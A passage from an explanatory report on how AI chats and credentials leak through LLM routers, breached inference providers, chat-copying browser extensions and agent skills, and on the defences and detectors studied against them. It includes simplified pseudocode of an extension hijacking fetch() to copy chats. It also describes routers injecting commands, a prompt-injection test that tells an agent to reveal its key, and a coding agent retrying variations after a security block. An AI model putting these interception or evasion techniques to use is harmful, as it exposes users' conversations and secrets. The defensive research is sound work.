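Liu's team also received other people's conversations. They set up poorly secured decoy routers on 20 domains and 20 IP addresses, and strangers added them to routes that real coding agents were using. The decoys handled about two billion tokens and 440 Codex sessions, which exposed 99 credentials. In 401 of the sessions, the agent was set to run commands without asking its user. The SANS honeypot had received one such session.

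According to *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet*, the researchers kept only totals and scrambled identifiers. They could have kept everything, and the developers would have had no way to tell. A developer chooses only the first router, which may buy its access from a reseller that buys it from another reseller. Each of these services can read the whole conversation.

### What a used canary proves

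Moore, of the security company Dragos, describes a much larger canary test in *Three breaches, endless leaks* (2026). From July to November, his team sent nearly two million prompts to widely used AI services. *Researcher Planted 2 Million Fake Secrets in AI Prompts* (Faisal, 2026) lists AWS keys, SSH passwords (for logging in to a remote machine), web addresses and references to private code repositories among the planted secrets. The team used each secret only once, in one prompt to one provider.

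*Dragos planted 2m secrets in AI prompts and caught 3 hacked providers* (Constantin, 2026) reports that attackers had broken into three companies that host models, and that none of them knew until Dragos told them. In the largest breach, the attackers copied every request that Dragos sent during a few short periods in late October. They tested some of the planted keys within hours and tried to add their own users to the AWS accounts. Real customers' requests were passing through the same systems, so the attackers almost certainly copied those too.

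Some of the stolen requests carried a Zero Data Retention (ZDR) setting, under which the provider shouldn't routinely store prompts and responses after processing them. The setting can't stop an intruder from copying a request while the provider is handling it, a limitation Moore also pointed out.

OpenRouter, a large router that had been sending requests to some of the affected companies, describes its response in *Data Processing Incidents on Inference Providers* (2026). It removed three providers and withdrew ZDR status from 125 endpoints, some of them as a precaution. It said the findings showed no breach of its own systems. *Data processing incidents at the inference providers behind OpenRouter* (2026), an article by the anoni.net community, notes that OpenRouter had not named the three providers by 1 December.

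Other leaks needed no break-in. The article's Chinese version, *OpenRouter 背後推論供應商的資料處理事件* (2026), describes a marketplace where the seller with the lowest price handles each request. A seller could read and keep customers' prompts by switching on request logs. The sellers the researchers traced seemed to be individuals on home internet connections. The researchers detected them through their attempts to log in to Dragos's test servers, and would not have noticed a seller who only saved the prompts.

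A used canary shows that someone or something read the prompt, but may not show who or why. MiniMax, a Chinese AI company, said its security monitoring had extracted web addresses from some requests and automatically visited some of them, including addresses from requests marked ZDR. It said it had found no other disclosure of prompts or responses to third parties. MiniMax has since switched the system off on the affected routes and deleted the stored addresses. Its customers hadn't agreed to the monitoring, but an automated visit to a web address is much weaker evidence of theft than someone using a stolen key to add users to an account.

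It can also be hard to tell where on the route a leak happened. If Ana sends a canary through a router to a provider and someone later uses it, she knows which request leaked, but either company could have leaked it. She could send a second canary straight to the same provider. If someone uses both, the provider is the more likely source. If repeated tests expose only the canaries sent through the router, the leak is probably at the router or another server behind it.

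### Checking, logging and signing replies

Liu's team tested three defences that a client can use without help from the router or provider, all on artificial data. Two of them inspect what the router sends back, so they don't affect what it keeps. One of these blocks shell commands that download from unapproved sites or install unapproved packages. It stopped all 1,000 malicious samples and wrongly blocked 1% of harmless commands, but it failed every time in a further test against an attacker who knew how it worked. The other flags unusual tool calls. It caught 89% of the simplest malicious samples and wrongly flagged 6.7% of harmless ones.

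The third defence is to log each request and response, along with the router's address. This doesn't prevent theft, but if Ana later learns that a router was stealing keys, she can find which of her keys passed through it and replace them. The log would show which source code the router had seen, although exposed code can't be replaced like a key. The log also needs protection because it contains another copy of the conversation.

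None of these defences can prove that a tool call came from the model, so Liu and colleagues propose that providers sign their replies:

1. The client includes a new random number in its request.
2. The provider signs the model's name, the tool call, the reason the reply ended and the random number, using a private key that only the provider holds.
3. The router passes on the reply and the signature.
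4. The client checks the signature with the provider's public key before running the tool.

If the router changes the command, the check fails. The random number prevents the router from substituting an older signed reply. But if the router copies the conversation and passes the reply on unchanged, the signature is still valid. By the time the provider signs the reply, the router has already read Ana's prompt, her files and any passwords in them.

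Signing also causes problems for honest routers that convert replies between providers' formats, because the converted reply no longer matches the signature. *AEX* (2026) proposes linking each reply to its request and recording changes that the client has agreed to accept, so that those changes don't look like tampering.

*RFC 9421* already defines a standard way to sign web messages, but major providers weren't signing their tool calls when Liu and colleagues checked.

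### Encrypting the conversation past the router

To stop the router from reading the conversation, Ana's client could encrypt it with a key that only the provider can unlock. The model's name and the billing details would stay outside the encrypted part. The router could then do only some of its usual work:

| Router's job | Possible if it can't read the conversation? |
|---|---|
| Check the user's credential and spending limit | Yes |
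| Attach the provider's key | Yes |
| Charge by the token | Yes, if the provider reports the count separately |
| Choose a model according to the question | No |
| Convert between providers' formats | No |
| Remove passwords or personal data | No |
| Keep full logs for compliance | No |
| Switch to another provider after a failure | Only if the client encrypts the request again for that provider |

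Encrypting the conversation so that only the provider can read it might be a good trade for a freelancer who uses a router because it is cheap. Ana's employer would probably reject it, since companies install gateways partly to log requests. Every provider would also have to support the scheme, and the router would still see the size and timing of each message. Encryption would hide the conversation from a dishonest reseller, but the provider has to decrypt it to run the model, so an intruder at the provider could still read it.

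### What attestation proves

The enclave-based router by Xie and colleagues hides conversations from its operator without requiring any change by the provider. It relies on attestation, in which the hardware signs a statement about the code it is running:

1. The operator publishes the router's source code and records the release in a public log.
2. The client's owner, or a coding agent acting for them, reads the code, builds the program from it and computes the program's cryptographic fingerprint.
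3. When the client connects, the enclave returns a signed document containing the fingerprint of the running program, a random number the client has just chosen and a fingerprint of the connection's certificate.
4. The client sends the conversation only if the signature is valid and all three values match.

If the hardware is sound, this proves that the program Ana inspected is running in a genuine enclave at the other end of her connection. A program that saves every conversation could also pass if Ana missed the code that does so when she inspected it.

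Xie and colleagues made the code easier to check by keeping only 851 lines inside the enclave. This part stores nothing between requests and can send conversations only to addresses built into the program. The operator can choose a provider from that list but can't add a server of its own. In a small trial, the researchers planted ten violations of the security rules in the code and asked two coding agents to find them. One found all ten and the other found eight.

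Like encryption to the provider, this design gives up format conversion, content rewriting and conversation logging. Unlike that scheme, it can try another approved provider after a failure, because the enclave can read the request. *Evidence-Bound Gateway-Path Provenance for Third-Party LLM Inference* (2026) proposes a more flexible gateway that makes routing and pricing decisions inside the enclave. The client sets limits in advance, and a signed record at the end shows which permitted route the request took. This gateway needs more code inside the enclave, so Ana has more to check.

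Attestation also depends on the hardware keeping its signing key secret. According to *πCreds* (2026), physical attacks that extract such keys are practical and completely invalidate the guarantee. Xie and colleagues exclude physical attacks from their analysis. They ran their router on Amazon's servers, which an ordinary operator can't physically reach, but a reseller that ran the router on its own machines could physically reach them.

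An operator also has to choose to offer attestation, and one that makes money from customers' transcripts has good reason not to. Ana could use only routers that offer it, but this would rule out honest routers that haven't adopted it.

Xie and colleagues assume that the provider is honest. Their enclave decrypts the conversation and forwards it in a form the provider can read. An attested router in front of one of the three companies in Moore's study would have delivered Ana's prompts, unaltered, to a company that attackers had already breached.

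## Browser extensions that copy chats to a second server

A secure router can't protect a conversation that leaks from the user's browser. Browser extensions are small programs that add features to a browser, and many have permission to read every page the user opens. They run at the user's end of the TLS connection, where the chat is in plain text. Expel's *On the radar* describes several dozen incidents in one month in which Chrome extensions copied AI chats to outside servers.

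Researchers have documented three cases in some detail. OX Security's *900K Users Compromised* covers two extensions that imitated a chat sidebar from the company AITOPIA. Koi Security examined Urban VPN Proxy, a free service that routes web traffic through other servers to hide the user's location. The third case is Prompt Optimizer – SecondBrain, an extension that offers to improve the wording of prompts. 24 Канал's *Chrome SecondBrain тайно похищает чаты ChatGPT и Copilot* (2026), a Ukrainian news report, credits the researcher Jean Marie with reverse-engineering it. ThreatCluster's *Chrome Extension Steals AI Prompts from 100k Users Across Multiple Platforms* summarises the same research.

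| | AITOPIA look-alikes | Urban VPN Proxy | SecondBrain |
|---|---|---|---|
| Users | About 900,000 | About 6 million on Chrome and 1.3 million on Edge | About 100,000 |
| Chatbots covered | ChatGPT and DeepSeek | Eight | Nine |
| Data taken | Messages, conversation identifiers, times, and the addresses of all open tabs | Prompts, replies, identifiers, times, session details, and the chatbot and model used | Prompts and replies |
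| Destination | `deepaichats.com` and `chatsaigpt.com` | Servers under `urban-vpn.com` | The developer's server |
| Timing | Every 30 minutes | Continuously, even with the VPN off | From the moment a chatbot page loads |
| Purpose given to users | Anonymous analytics | Protection on the setup screen, marketing in the privacy policy | None, because the store listing said it collected no data |

### From the page to the collector

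The AITOPIA look-alikes read conversations from the displayed page. OX Security and G DATA's *Browser Spy-Ons* (2026) describe the steps:

1. The extension checks whether the page's address contains "chatgpt" or "deepseek".
2. It watches the page for new messages and waits until the chatbot has finished its reply.
3. It saves the latest question and answer in the browser's local storage, along with the conversation's identifier.
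4. It sends the stored data to the collector in batches.

The uploads used Base64, a common way of writing data as plain characters, which anyone can decode. In one upload that G DATA decoded, the `qus` and `answer` fields held web addresses, and the conversation was in `chatArray`. Microsoft found activity from these extensions in more than 20,000 organisations' accounts. According to Microsoft, the uploads resembled routine browser traffic, and the extension cleared its stored data after each one, which left less evidence on the computer.

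Urban VPN and SecondBrain intercept the data that passes between the page and the chatbot. When a user opens ChatGPT, for example, Urban VPN adds a script to the page that replaces `fetch()`, a browser function for sending requests and receiving replies. A simplified version looks like this:

```
original_fetch = page.fetch

page.fetch = function(request):
    reply = original_fetch(request)
    copy_to_extension(request, reply)
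    return reply
```

The page calls the new function as if it were the old one. The script picks out the prompts and replies, and a background process compresses them and sends them to Urban VPN.

SecondBrain also intercepts WebSockets, which are connections that stay open so both sides can send messages at any time. The script that does this is called `chatgpt_context_fetch_diagnostics.js`, which sounds like a debugging tool. It can read the message format used by Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's assistant for organisations, so a company that has made Copilot its approved AI service could still have its employees' chats copied to a second server.

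SecondBrain encrypts the chats before sending them, but its servers issue the key, so the company can read them. The encryption mainly stops other people from reading them, including a network administrator checking what the extension sends.

### The copy the chatbot doesn't need

Deleting the `copy_to_extension` line from the code above would not change how the chatbot works, but deleting a client's request to an LLM proxy would leave the user without an answer, because the request reaches the model through the proxy.

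```
LLM PROXY     user <====> proxy <====> provider

EXTENSION     user <=================> provider
                |
                +------> collector
```

The chatbot already receives the message, so the extra copy sent to the collector must serve some purpose other than getting a reply. A researcher can check this by blocking the collector's address and seeing whether the chatbot still answers.

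A second recipient is especially suspicious when the extension's advertised function has nothing to do with chats. OffSeq's *PromptSnatcher* describes two ad blockers, with 90,000 installs between them, that copied every prompt and reply on eight chatbots. On five of those chatbots, the extensions also checked whether the user had a paid account. Blocking ads requires none of this information. According to Notebookcheck, the Firefox versions claimed to collect no data.

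Urban VPN advertises an "AI protection" feature that warns users about personal data in their prompts and suspicious links in the replies. Koi found that the extension kept copying chats when this feature was turned off, so the feature can't explain the copying. The feature does have to read the chat, but it could look for an email address or phone number without sending the conversation anywhere.

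Looking for a second recipient won't catch every theft. The AITOPIA look-alikes also had a working chat sidebar, whose operator would be the first recipient of anything typed there. The genuine AITOPIA states in its privacy policy that it saves sidebar chats on its servers, a practice OX Security considers legitimate. A dishonest operator could save the same chats for resale without sending an extra copy from the browser. An extension could also defeat the blocking test by withholding the chatbot's reply until the collector had received its copy.

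Researchers can easily confuse an extension that copies conversations from other chatbots with a client for a new chat service. G DATA's third example, an extension called Chat AI, is listed among those that steal conversations, but the behaviour G DATA describes is different. Chat AI displays a chat page hosted at a recently registered web address and shares preferences such as language, theme and username with that page. An honest client for a new chat service could do the same. The new address is a reason to investigate, but it doesn't show that Chat AI copied conversations from other chatbots.

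### Tools that have a reason to copy

Some extensions need a second recipient to do their job:

| Tool | What it may need to send | When | What would be out of place |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt optimiser | The draft prompt and perhaps some earlier messages | When the user asks for a rewrite | Chats in which nobody used the optimiser |
| Translator | The text to translate, possibly every reply | On request, or as each message appears | Account details, or a permanent archive of the text |
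| Backup tool | Every message, with dates and identifiers | Continuously or on a schedule | A copy in a stranger's account |

A prompt optimiser usually has to send the draft to a model that can rewrite it. ExtScope's *Prompt Optimizer* reproduces SecondBrain's store description, which calls the product "transparent" and promises to improve prompts "in one click", so a click would be a natural time to send a copy. SecondBrain could correctly argue that some prompts need the earlier conversation for a good rewrite, but this wouldn't explain why the extension sent chats when nobody had asked for one. According to ThreatCluster, the extension also collected chats in a fresh browser profile without any action by the user.

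A translator is harder to judge. One that uses a server to translate every ChatGPT reply into Spanish sends each complete reply there as it appears, with no further clicks, much as SecondBrain does. The returned translation shows that the request had a use, but a thief could provide translations too. Some translators can run entirely in the browser, though a developer might reasonably prefer a larger model on a server. If the translation service needs the text, the judgment depends on what its operator does with it afterwards.

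A chat backup tool has to copy almost everything that Urban VPN took. LLMemory saves chats from ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and other services to the user's own Google Drive or a private GitHub repository, and its developer says nothing passes through the company's servers. Users install such a tool to get a second copy of their chats, so an investigator can infer very little from the fact that one exists.

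The destination is more useful here, although the host name may not be enough. An extension that saved chats to an attacker's Google Drive would also contact Google, so the investigator would have to check which account receives the files. A destination the user doesn't control may still be legitimate, because a backup company might store chats on its own server with the user's full agreement.

### Does a line in a privacy policy count as consent?

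Urban VPN is a better example of disclosed collection than the other two cases. SecondBrain denied collecting data, and 24 Канал reports that the extension's configuration file switched the consent settings on at every start. The AITOPIA look-alikes asked to collect "anonymous, non-identifiable analytics data", then took full conversations. According to the privacy policy for one of them, all information stayed in the browser. Users could refuse, but Microsoft found that later updates turned the collection back on. Microsoft also saw AI-driven browsers install these extensions without users' explicit approval.

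Urban VPN disclosed more. Its setup screen listed "ChatAI communication" among the data it processed. According to The Hacker News' *Featured Chrome Browser Extension* (2025), the company updated its privacy policy on 25 June 2025, two weeks before releasing the version that copied chats. In the policy, the company said it collected prompts and outputs and disclosed prompts "for marketing analytics purposes". It also said it shared browsing data, including the chats, with its affiliate BiScience, a data broker.

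Urban VPN didn't reply when Tom's Guide asked why it collected and sold data, but its documents suggest a defence. Users get a free VPN, and the company states in writing what it collects and says it tries to filter identifying details out of prompts. *Urban Shield*, its listing for a Firefox extension, describes the collection of browsing data as "subject to your consent through the prominent notice". Tom's Guide's 2026 review, *Urban VPN has released its own in-house protocol*, says users can withdraw consent and the company's website has a "Do not sell" page. Urban VPN could also argue that few people read the terms of any online service, so if consent required careful reading, much of the consent on the web would be invalid.

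Koi's main objection is that many users never saw the relevant notice. Chrome and Edge update extensions automatically, so people who had installed an earlier version received the copying code in July without seeing the new setup screen. New users saw the screen, but it described the processing as a way "to provide these protections", and only the privacy policy mentioned marketing. They also couldn't use the VPN without accepting the chat collection. Koi found no setting that stopped the collection, so the right to withdraw consent may have been hard to exercise.

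Tom's Guide's *This VPN is harvesting your AI conversations* quotes a declaration in the store listing that Urban VPN didn't use or transfer data for purposes unrelated to the product's core functionality. Selling insights from chats is hard to reconcile with that. Malwarebytes' *Chrome extension slurps up AI chats after users installed it for privacy* (2025) acknowledges that the company "technically disclosed" the collection, but argues that few users would have expected it or agreed to it if they had understood it.

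The critics have the stronger case. ChatGPT users know that ChatGPT receives their messages, even if they never read its terms, but installing a VPN gives them no reason to expect that a data broker will too. Users who got the code through an update hadn't meaningfully authorised the transfer. Those who saw the setup screen had agreed to some processing of their chats, but hadn't knowingly agreed to their use for marketing.

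Google's *Disclosure Requirements* for Chrome extensions support this view. Developers must prominently disclose what they collect, how they will use it, and any later changes. They must also obtain "affirmative and informed consent" before installation. A sentence deep in a privacy policy doesn't meet that standard. The 2022 version exempted data closely related to a product's advertised function, but collecting AI chats has little to do with providing a VPN.

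Similarweb, which measures website traffic, is an even better example of disclosed collection. The Hacker News (2026) reports that Similarweb's browser extension, which has about a million users, gained the ability to monitor AI chats in May 2025. On 1 January 2026, Similarweb added a pop-up with its full terms of service, which made explicit that the extension collects data entered into AI tools. Its privacy policy also covers replies and uploaded files.

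Someone who accepts that pop-up has a much weaker claim to have been deceived than an Urban VPN user, especially since Similarweb's business is collecting data about web use. But the pop-up arrived about seven months after the monitoring feature, so it isn't evidence that earlier users had agreed. It is also easy to accept long terms without reading them. Similarweb uses some of the same interception methods as Urban VPN, so a reader couldn't tell from the code alone which company had explained its practices better.

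### What the browser stores checked

Urban VPN had a rating of 4.7 stars from 58,000 reviews and a "Featured" badge, which Google awards only after its store team has reviewed an extension. Koi argues that Google's reviewers either missed the copying code or didn't consider it a problem. They may instead have awarded the badge before the July update, in which case their review didn't cover the new code.

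The extension copied chats for more than five months before Koi published its findings in December 2025. Google then withdrew the badge, and a day later the extension was gone from the Chrome store. Koi couldn't tell whether Google or the developer had removed it. Microsoft said it was investigating, and by 23 December the extension was gone from the Edge store too.

OX Security reported the AITOPIA look-alikes to Google on 29 December 2025. Google replied the next day that it was reviewing the report. Both extensions were still available then, and one still had its Featured badge. That extension later lost the badge, and SecurityWeek's *Chrome Extensions With 900,000 Downloads Caught Stealing AI Chats* reports that both are no longer in the store. Uninstalling one of them opened a page offering the other. Neither 24 Канал nor ThreatCluster reports a response from Google or the developer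 about SecondBrain.

Even a careful review of an extension's files has limits. Similarweb's extension downloads a configuration file with instructions for extracting chats from ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and Perplexity, so the company could change those instructions without submitting a new version to the store. John Tuckner of the security company Secure Annex told The Hacker News that it was unclear whether this broke Google's rules on loading code dynamically and limiting each extension to a single purpose.

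Google has since tightened its rules on data collection, in an update announced on 1 July (Walton, 2026, *Chrome Web Store policy updates*). From 1 August, developers may collect only data strictly necessary for an extension's disclosed single purpose, and may no longer gather extra data for unrelated analytics or advertising (CyberInsider, 2026). This makes Urban VPN's case easier to decide, because a VPN doesn't need to collect AI chats, whatever its users have accepted. But a backup tool could still copy every message, and Similarweb could argue that measuring the use of AI tools is part of its purpose.

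Under the new rule, a developer can still invent a purpose to justify collecting data. In January 2025, an anonymous researcher accused BiScience and its partners of doing this with browsing history, by adding features that supposedly needed the history so that they could claim an exception for data necessary to the product. A developer who wanted people's chats could likewise add a prompt optimiser or a backup button, and the store's reviewers would have to decide whether the feature needed every conversation.

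## What network monitoring and sandbox tests can see

Without relying on a store's reviewers, a company can monitor its computers' network connections and run suspicious programs in a sandbox before anyone installs them. Both methods record what software does, so they can catch an upload that the code disguises or the description leaves out. But they only observe the user's end of the connection, so they can't detect the copies a proxy operator keeps on its server.

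### What encryption leaves visible

Someone who watches an encrypted connection can see the server's address, how much data passes in each direction, and when. They can usually see the server's name too, because TLS normally sends it unencrypted at the start. A newer standard, Encrypted Client Hello, hides the name, but *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) notes that the address or the computer's earlier lookup of the name may still reveal it. A monitor on the user's machine can also record which program opened the connection and who was running it.

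Some companies decrypt their employees' web traffic to inspect it, so they can read the transcripts. This would reveal a leaked password, but it may not show whether the recipient is a legitimate proxy or a thief, since both can receive the same transcript.

Packet sizes and timing reveal a surprising amount without any decryption. Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, sent 60 prompts to each of ten models 100 times and trained classifiers on the encrypted traffic:

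| What the classifier had to identify | Accuracy | Random guessing |
|---|---|---|
| Which of ten models was answering | 97.7% | 10% |
| Which of six types of prompt the user had sent | 76.7% | 16.7% |
| Which of ten tasks a team of agents was doing | Up to 90.7% | 10% |

This works because the server sends each piece of a reply as soon as the model generates it. Models split text differently and run at different speeds, so each produces its own pattern of message sizes and gaps between messages.

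The test was easier than real monitoring because the classifier only had to choose from a fixed list of models, and the researchers assumed that the observer knew where each interaction began and ended. Rewording the prompts lowered the classifier's accuracy at identifying models from 93.2% to 69.5%.

Canale and Soulis report that one group used the sizes of the streamed pieces to reconstruct 27% of AI assistants' replies and infer the topic of 53%. AgentPrint, the method in *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (2025), identifies which agent produced the traffic. None of these attacks reveals what the recipient does with a conversation.

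Traffic volume could expose a server that only stores transcripts. A transcript of 100,000 tokens is roughly 400 kilobytes of English text. After receiving it, a proxy would typically stream back a reply in many small pieces, while the storage-only server might return a one-line acknowledgement. However, a backup service would produce the same pattern, and the traffic of a collector that also returned real replies would look like a proxy's.

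### Alerts for unfamiliar domains

Elastic, which makes software for searching security logs, publishes a rule for spotting AI programs on Macs that contact unfamiliar servers. The source file of Elastic's *GenAI Process Connection to Unusual Domain* (2025) shows how it works:

1. The rule searches the last nine minutes of connection logs. It runs every five minutes, according to Elastic's page for an earlier version.
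2. It keeps connections from listed programs, such as `claude`, `codex`, `cursor` and `ollama`.
3. It drops connections with no recorded domain name and those to familiar domains, such as `anthropic.com` and `github.com`.
4. It checks whether each remaining domain appeared in the previous seven days.
5. It raises an alert for any domain that didn't.

In short:

```
alert if  program is in AI_PROGRAMS
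     and  domain is not in FAMILIAR_DOMAINS
     and  domain is not in LAST_7_DAYS
```

Elastic's guide *New terms rules* explains that these rules can also look for new combinations, such as a user's first login to a particular computer. This one checks only the domain, so if one developer connects to a dishonest router on Monday, a colleague on another Mac can connect to it on Tuesday without causing an alert.

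Here is how the rule would handle three cases on a company's Macs:

| Case | Listed program? | New domain? | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ana's employer moves its gateway to a new address | Yes, `claude` | Yes | False alarm |
| A developer uses a dishonest router every day | Yes, `codex` | No | No alert |
| An agent runs a Python script that uploads the conversation to a new server | No, `python3` | Yes | No alert |

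The gateway would trigger one alert, then no more as long as somebody used it at least once a week. It could trigger another after a two-week company holiday.

The dishonest operator's router may have triggered an alert on the first day. If the operator only began keeping conversations a month later, the rule would have alerted a month too early.

The rule misses the script's traffic because its list of programs doesn't include Python, Node.js or the download tool `curl`. It would usually miss traffic from Relay To Agent's script too, since that script is a JavaScript file that would normally run in Node.js. Adding these programs to the list would allow the rule to detect this traffic, but developers use them to contact all kinds of servers, so false alarms would probably increase sharply.

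The list of familiar domains leaves another gap because it includes every address ending in `amazonaws.com` or `azure.com`. This prevents many pointless alerts, but it also prevents alerts about data sent to storage that a thief rents from Amazon.

Elastic warns of false alarms, since developers who test new AI integrations "will naturally trigger alerts" and vendors sometimes move their services to new domains. It tells analysts to check who runs the domain, when it was registered, and whether the AI tool's configuration has recently changed.

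Elastic's *Connection to Common Large Language Model Endpoints* rule covers the reverse situation. It flags programs such as PowerShell, a Windows scripting tool, when they contact well-known model services, and Elastic labels the rule as noisy. Neither rule would flag a Python script that sends a conversation to an unknown server, because Python isn't on the first rule's list and the server isn't a well-known model service.

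### Ordinary agents that behave like attackers

Monitoring what programs do on a computer, as well as where they connect, produces false alarms of its own. The security company Sophos examined a week of alerts from customers' Windows computers in June 2026. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* describes several cases in which coding agents set off rules written to catch intruders:

- Codex tried to download the Python installer from Python's official website. Sophos blocked its first method, which attackers also use, so Codex tried several variations and then switched to another tool that attackers favour. Sophos blocked that too.
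- Claude Code used a browser-control skill that decrypted saved browser data through PowerShell. Sophos calls this "almost certainly benign" but thinks the rule was right to block it.
- Cursor, another coding agent, tried to add a script to the folder of programs that Windows runs at startup. Sophos couldn't determine why.

Sophos also has silent rules, which record behaviour without blocking it. Command-and-control rules, which detect communication between an attacker and a compromised computer, produced 34.0% of the silent alerts linked to agents, counted by machines affected. Agents often match these rules because they make many network calls and start many programs.

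The report gives percentages but no totals, so it can't show how often an agent causes a false alarm. None of its examples involves transcript forwarding, but they show why an analyst can't treat an alert about an agent as proof of an attack, even when the rule worked as intended. Turning the rules off for agents would also be risky, since an attacker who controlled an agent could then use the same methods unnoticed.

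### Detecting unapproved agents

Canale and Soulis set out to detect AI agents that employees use without their company's approval. They compare several places to look:

| Where the company looks | What it can see | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Its web proxy | The server that a computer contacts | The program responsible, and models that run on the computer itself |
| Encrypted traffic on the network | Patterns that suggest a model or task | The program and the user |
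| Its list of installed software | Known products | Home-made scripts, and whether anyone uses a product |
| The user's computer | Programs, users, settings and connections | Agents in virtual machines or in the cloud |

Agent Detector is a free Windows program that runs on the user's computer. Its main rule looks for a program that is connected to a model service and has started a command shell. It identifies services from a catalogue of 184 entries and also checks for base URL settings that point to unknown servers. It doesn't read conversations or block anything, but it shows the user a notice if it finds an unapproved agent.

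The researchers argue that behaviour alone can't identify an agent. They describe a running program *p* by two sets of features:

*x*(*p*) = (*β*(*p*), *ι*(*p*))

A detector can examine a program's behaviour, such as the timing of its connections and the other programs it starts, or its identity, such as the names of the software and the remote server. An agent and an ordinary automation script can behave identically. A detector that uses only behaviour must then give both the same result, so it either misses the agent or wrongly flags the script.

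Agent Detector was tested on 12 simulated agents and nine harmless workloads, each run five times. Three of the harmless workloads were copies of agents, changed to contact ordinary web services instead of models. Two simple behavioural rules flagged all three copies and a routine software installation. Agent Detector flagged none of the harmless workloads and found each of the 12 agents in most of its five runs, though it found two of them in only three. With administrator rights, it found 11 of the 12.

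Canale and Soulis acknowledge that these results overstate how well Agent Detector works. They had corrected the program after seeing earlier results from the same tests, and they scanned each agent within seconds of starting it. Agent Detector often identifies a model service from the computer's record of recent name lookups, which lasted no more than five minutes in their tests. An hourly scan would therefore usually miss an agent that kept one connection to such a service open. In a separate test, 15 of 40 scans at random moments detected an agent that connected only from time to time.

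The proxy tests are the most relevant to transcript forwarding. Agent Detector found an agent whose base URL setting pointed to an unknown relay, but missed one with the relay's address written into its code. An early version also flagged a harmless script because the script had inherited a base URL setting of the kind developers use to reach a company gateway.

Even a perfect detector would only recognise that an LLM was being used. It would judge whether that use was acceptable by checking the company's list of approved tools and servers. It would therefore miss an approved gateway whose operator sold the logs, and it would send a notice about a harmless relay that a developer had set up without approval.

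The argument about behaviour also applies to theft. Suppose Ana's router has kept no conversations for a year and starts keeping them today. The client behaves as before and connects to the same server, so *β* and *ι* are unchanged. Any detector that relies only on those two sets of features must give the same result as it did yesterday.

### Comparing a skill's description with its behaviour

A sandbox gives the tester more control than live monitoring, because the tester can plant data and see where it goes. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, took a random sample of 17,022 skills from the marketplace SkillsMP. Searches of the text and code narrowed these to 3,156 that might mishandle passwords or keys. The team then tested each one:

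1. They put the skill in an isolated container with Claude Code and fake credentials, which carried a marker unique to that skill.
2. They ran the skill three times on a task that matched its description.
3. They ran it three more times on material containing a malicious instruction, such as a web page that told the agent to reveal its key.
4. They recorded network traffic, file changes and printed output.
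5. If a credential leaked in at least two of the normal runs or one of the hostile runs, three researchers compared the skill's description with what it had done.

The sandbox flagged 1,427 skills. The reviewers judged 907 of them harmless, 437 careless and 83 malicious, so nearly two-thirds of the flags were false positives.

Almost all the difficult decisions involved 1,099 skills that sent or exposed credentials in normal runs but resisted the malicious instructions. An honest client for an LLM proxy would probably behave this way, because it has to send its key with every request. According to the paper, the sandbox couldn't distinguish authorised calls from exfiltration in this group, so reviewers had to decide whether each transfer was declared and necessary. They classified 907 skills as harmless, 181 as careless and 11 as malicious.

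Chen and colleagues report that 397 of the 520 careless or malicious skills (76.3%) could be detected only by reading the text and code together. For example, one skill offered weather forecasts while its script sent the user's credentials file to an outside address. Many clients normally send credentials off the machine, so a reviewer also needs the description to see that a weather tool had no reason to send that file.

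The 76.3% figure may overstate how often a reviewer needs both the code and the description. The most common problem, found in 352 skills, was code that printed secrets while it ran. At least 229 of those skills must be among the 397 behind the 76.3% figure, because the paper puts only 123 skills in its other two groups. A reviewer could often spot such a print command from the code alone. The description matters more for deciding whether a transfer to an outside server is legitimate.

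The study measured leaked credentials, not stolen transcripts. The two can overlap, for example when a skill prints a key, which then becomes part of the transcript. In 68 of the 520 skills, credentials went to servers that the researchers attributed to attackers.

A similar test for transcripts could plant a marked sentence in the conversation, but an agent sends the whole conversation to its model anyway. The tester would have to separate those expected requests from any others. Each container also ran for at most two minutes, so a skill that waited half an hour before its first upload would have leaked nothing during the test.

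### SkillSentry's matched runs

*SkillSentry* accounts for expected requests by running the same task with and without the skill. Before the runs, a language model identifies what the skill needs to do for its advertised purpose, looks for code or instructions that might do more than that, and designs a test for each suspicious behaviour.

Some skills misbehave only when they find something worth stealing, so SkillSentry also repeats the task in an environment with a decoy, such as a fake key that the task doesn't require. Each test therefore has four runs. Take an invented document formatter that uploads the conversation if it finds an API key:

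| | Without the skill | With the skill |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary environment | The agent formats the document | The agent formats the document |
| Environment with a fake key | The agent formats the document | The agent formats the document, and the skill uploads the conversation |

SkillSentry removes every effect that also occurs without the skill. If *E*(*w*, 1) is the set of completed effects in environment *w* with the skill, and *E*(*w*, 0) is the set without it, what remains is:

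*D*(*w*) = *E*(*w*, 1) − *E*(*w*, 0)

The agent's normal requests to its model occur in all four runs, so they cancel out, leaving the upload. SkillSentry reports the skill as unsafe if the upload succeeded, something in the skill's files explains it, and formatting a document doesn't require it. If a test never reaches the suspicious behaviour, SkillSentry reports the result as "unresolved" instead of safe.

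The paper compares SkillSentry with other scanners on two collections of harmful and harmless skills:

| Scanner | SkillTrustBench: harmful skills found | SkillTrustBench: harmless skills flagged | MalSkillBench: harmful skills found | MalSkillBench: harmless skills flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SkillSentry | 96.1% | 4.2% | 94.7% | 2.3% |
| SkillSpector with a language model | 91.2% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 20.9% |
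| Cisco's scanner with a language model | 97.0% | 53.7% | 96.2% | 38.8% |
| Skill Vetter on OpenClaw | 97.5% | 49.5% | 98.7% | 3.9% |

SkillSentry's main advantage is its low rate of false positives. Skill Vetter, which uses a language model to read the whole skill, found more of the harmful skills in both collections, and its false positive rate in MalSkillBench was almost as low.

The researchers also removed parts of SkillSentry to see what each contributed. The average share of harmless skills flagged rose from 3.24% to 10.00% without the comparison runs, and to 34.09% without the check that an effect had happened. When they ran skills without first studying the code, SkillSentry flagged no harmless skills but found only 8% of the harmful ones in SkillTrustBench and 4% in MalSkillBench, because ordinary tasks rarely triggered the hidden behaviour.

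Many of the rates in these experiments are multiples of 4%, which suggests samples of perhaps 25 or 50 skills, although the paper describes only its cost measurements as sampled. The difference between 3% and 10% is therefore uncertain, but the drop to 8% and 4% is too large to dismiss.

### A hidden collector and a proxy that keeps copies

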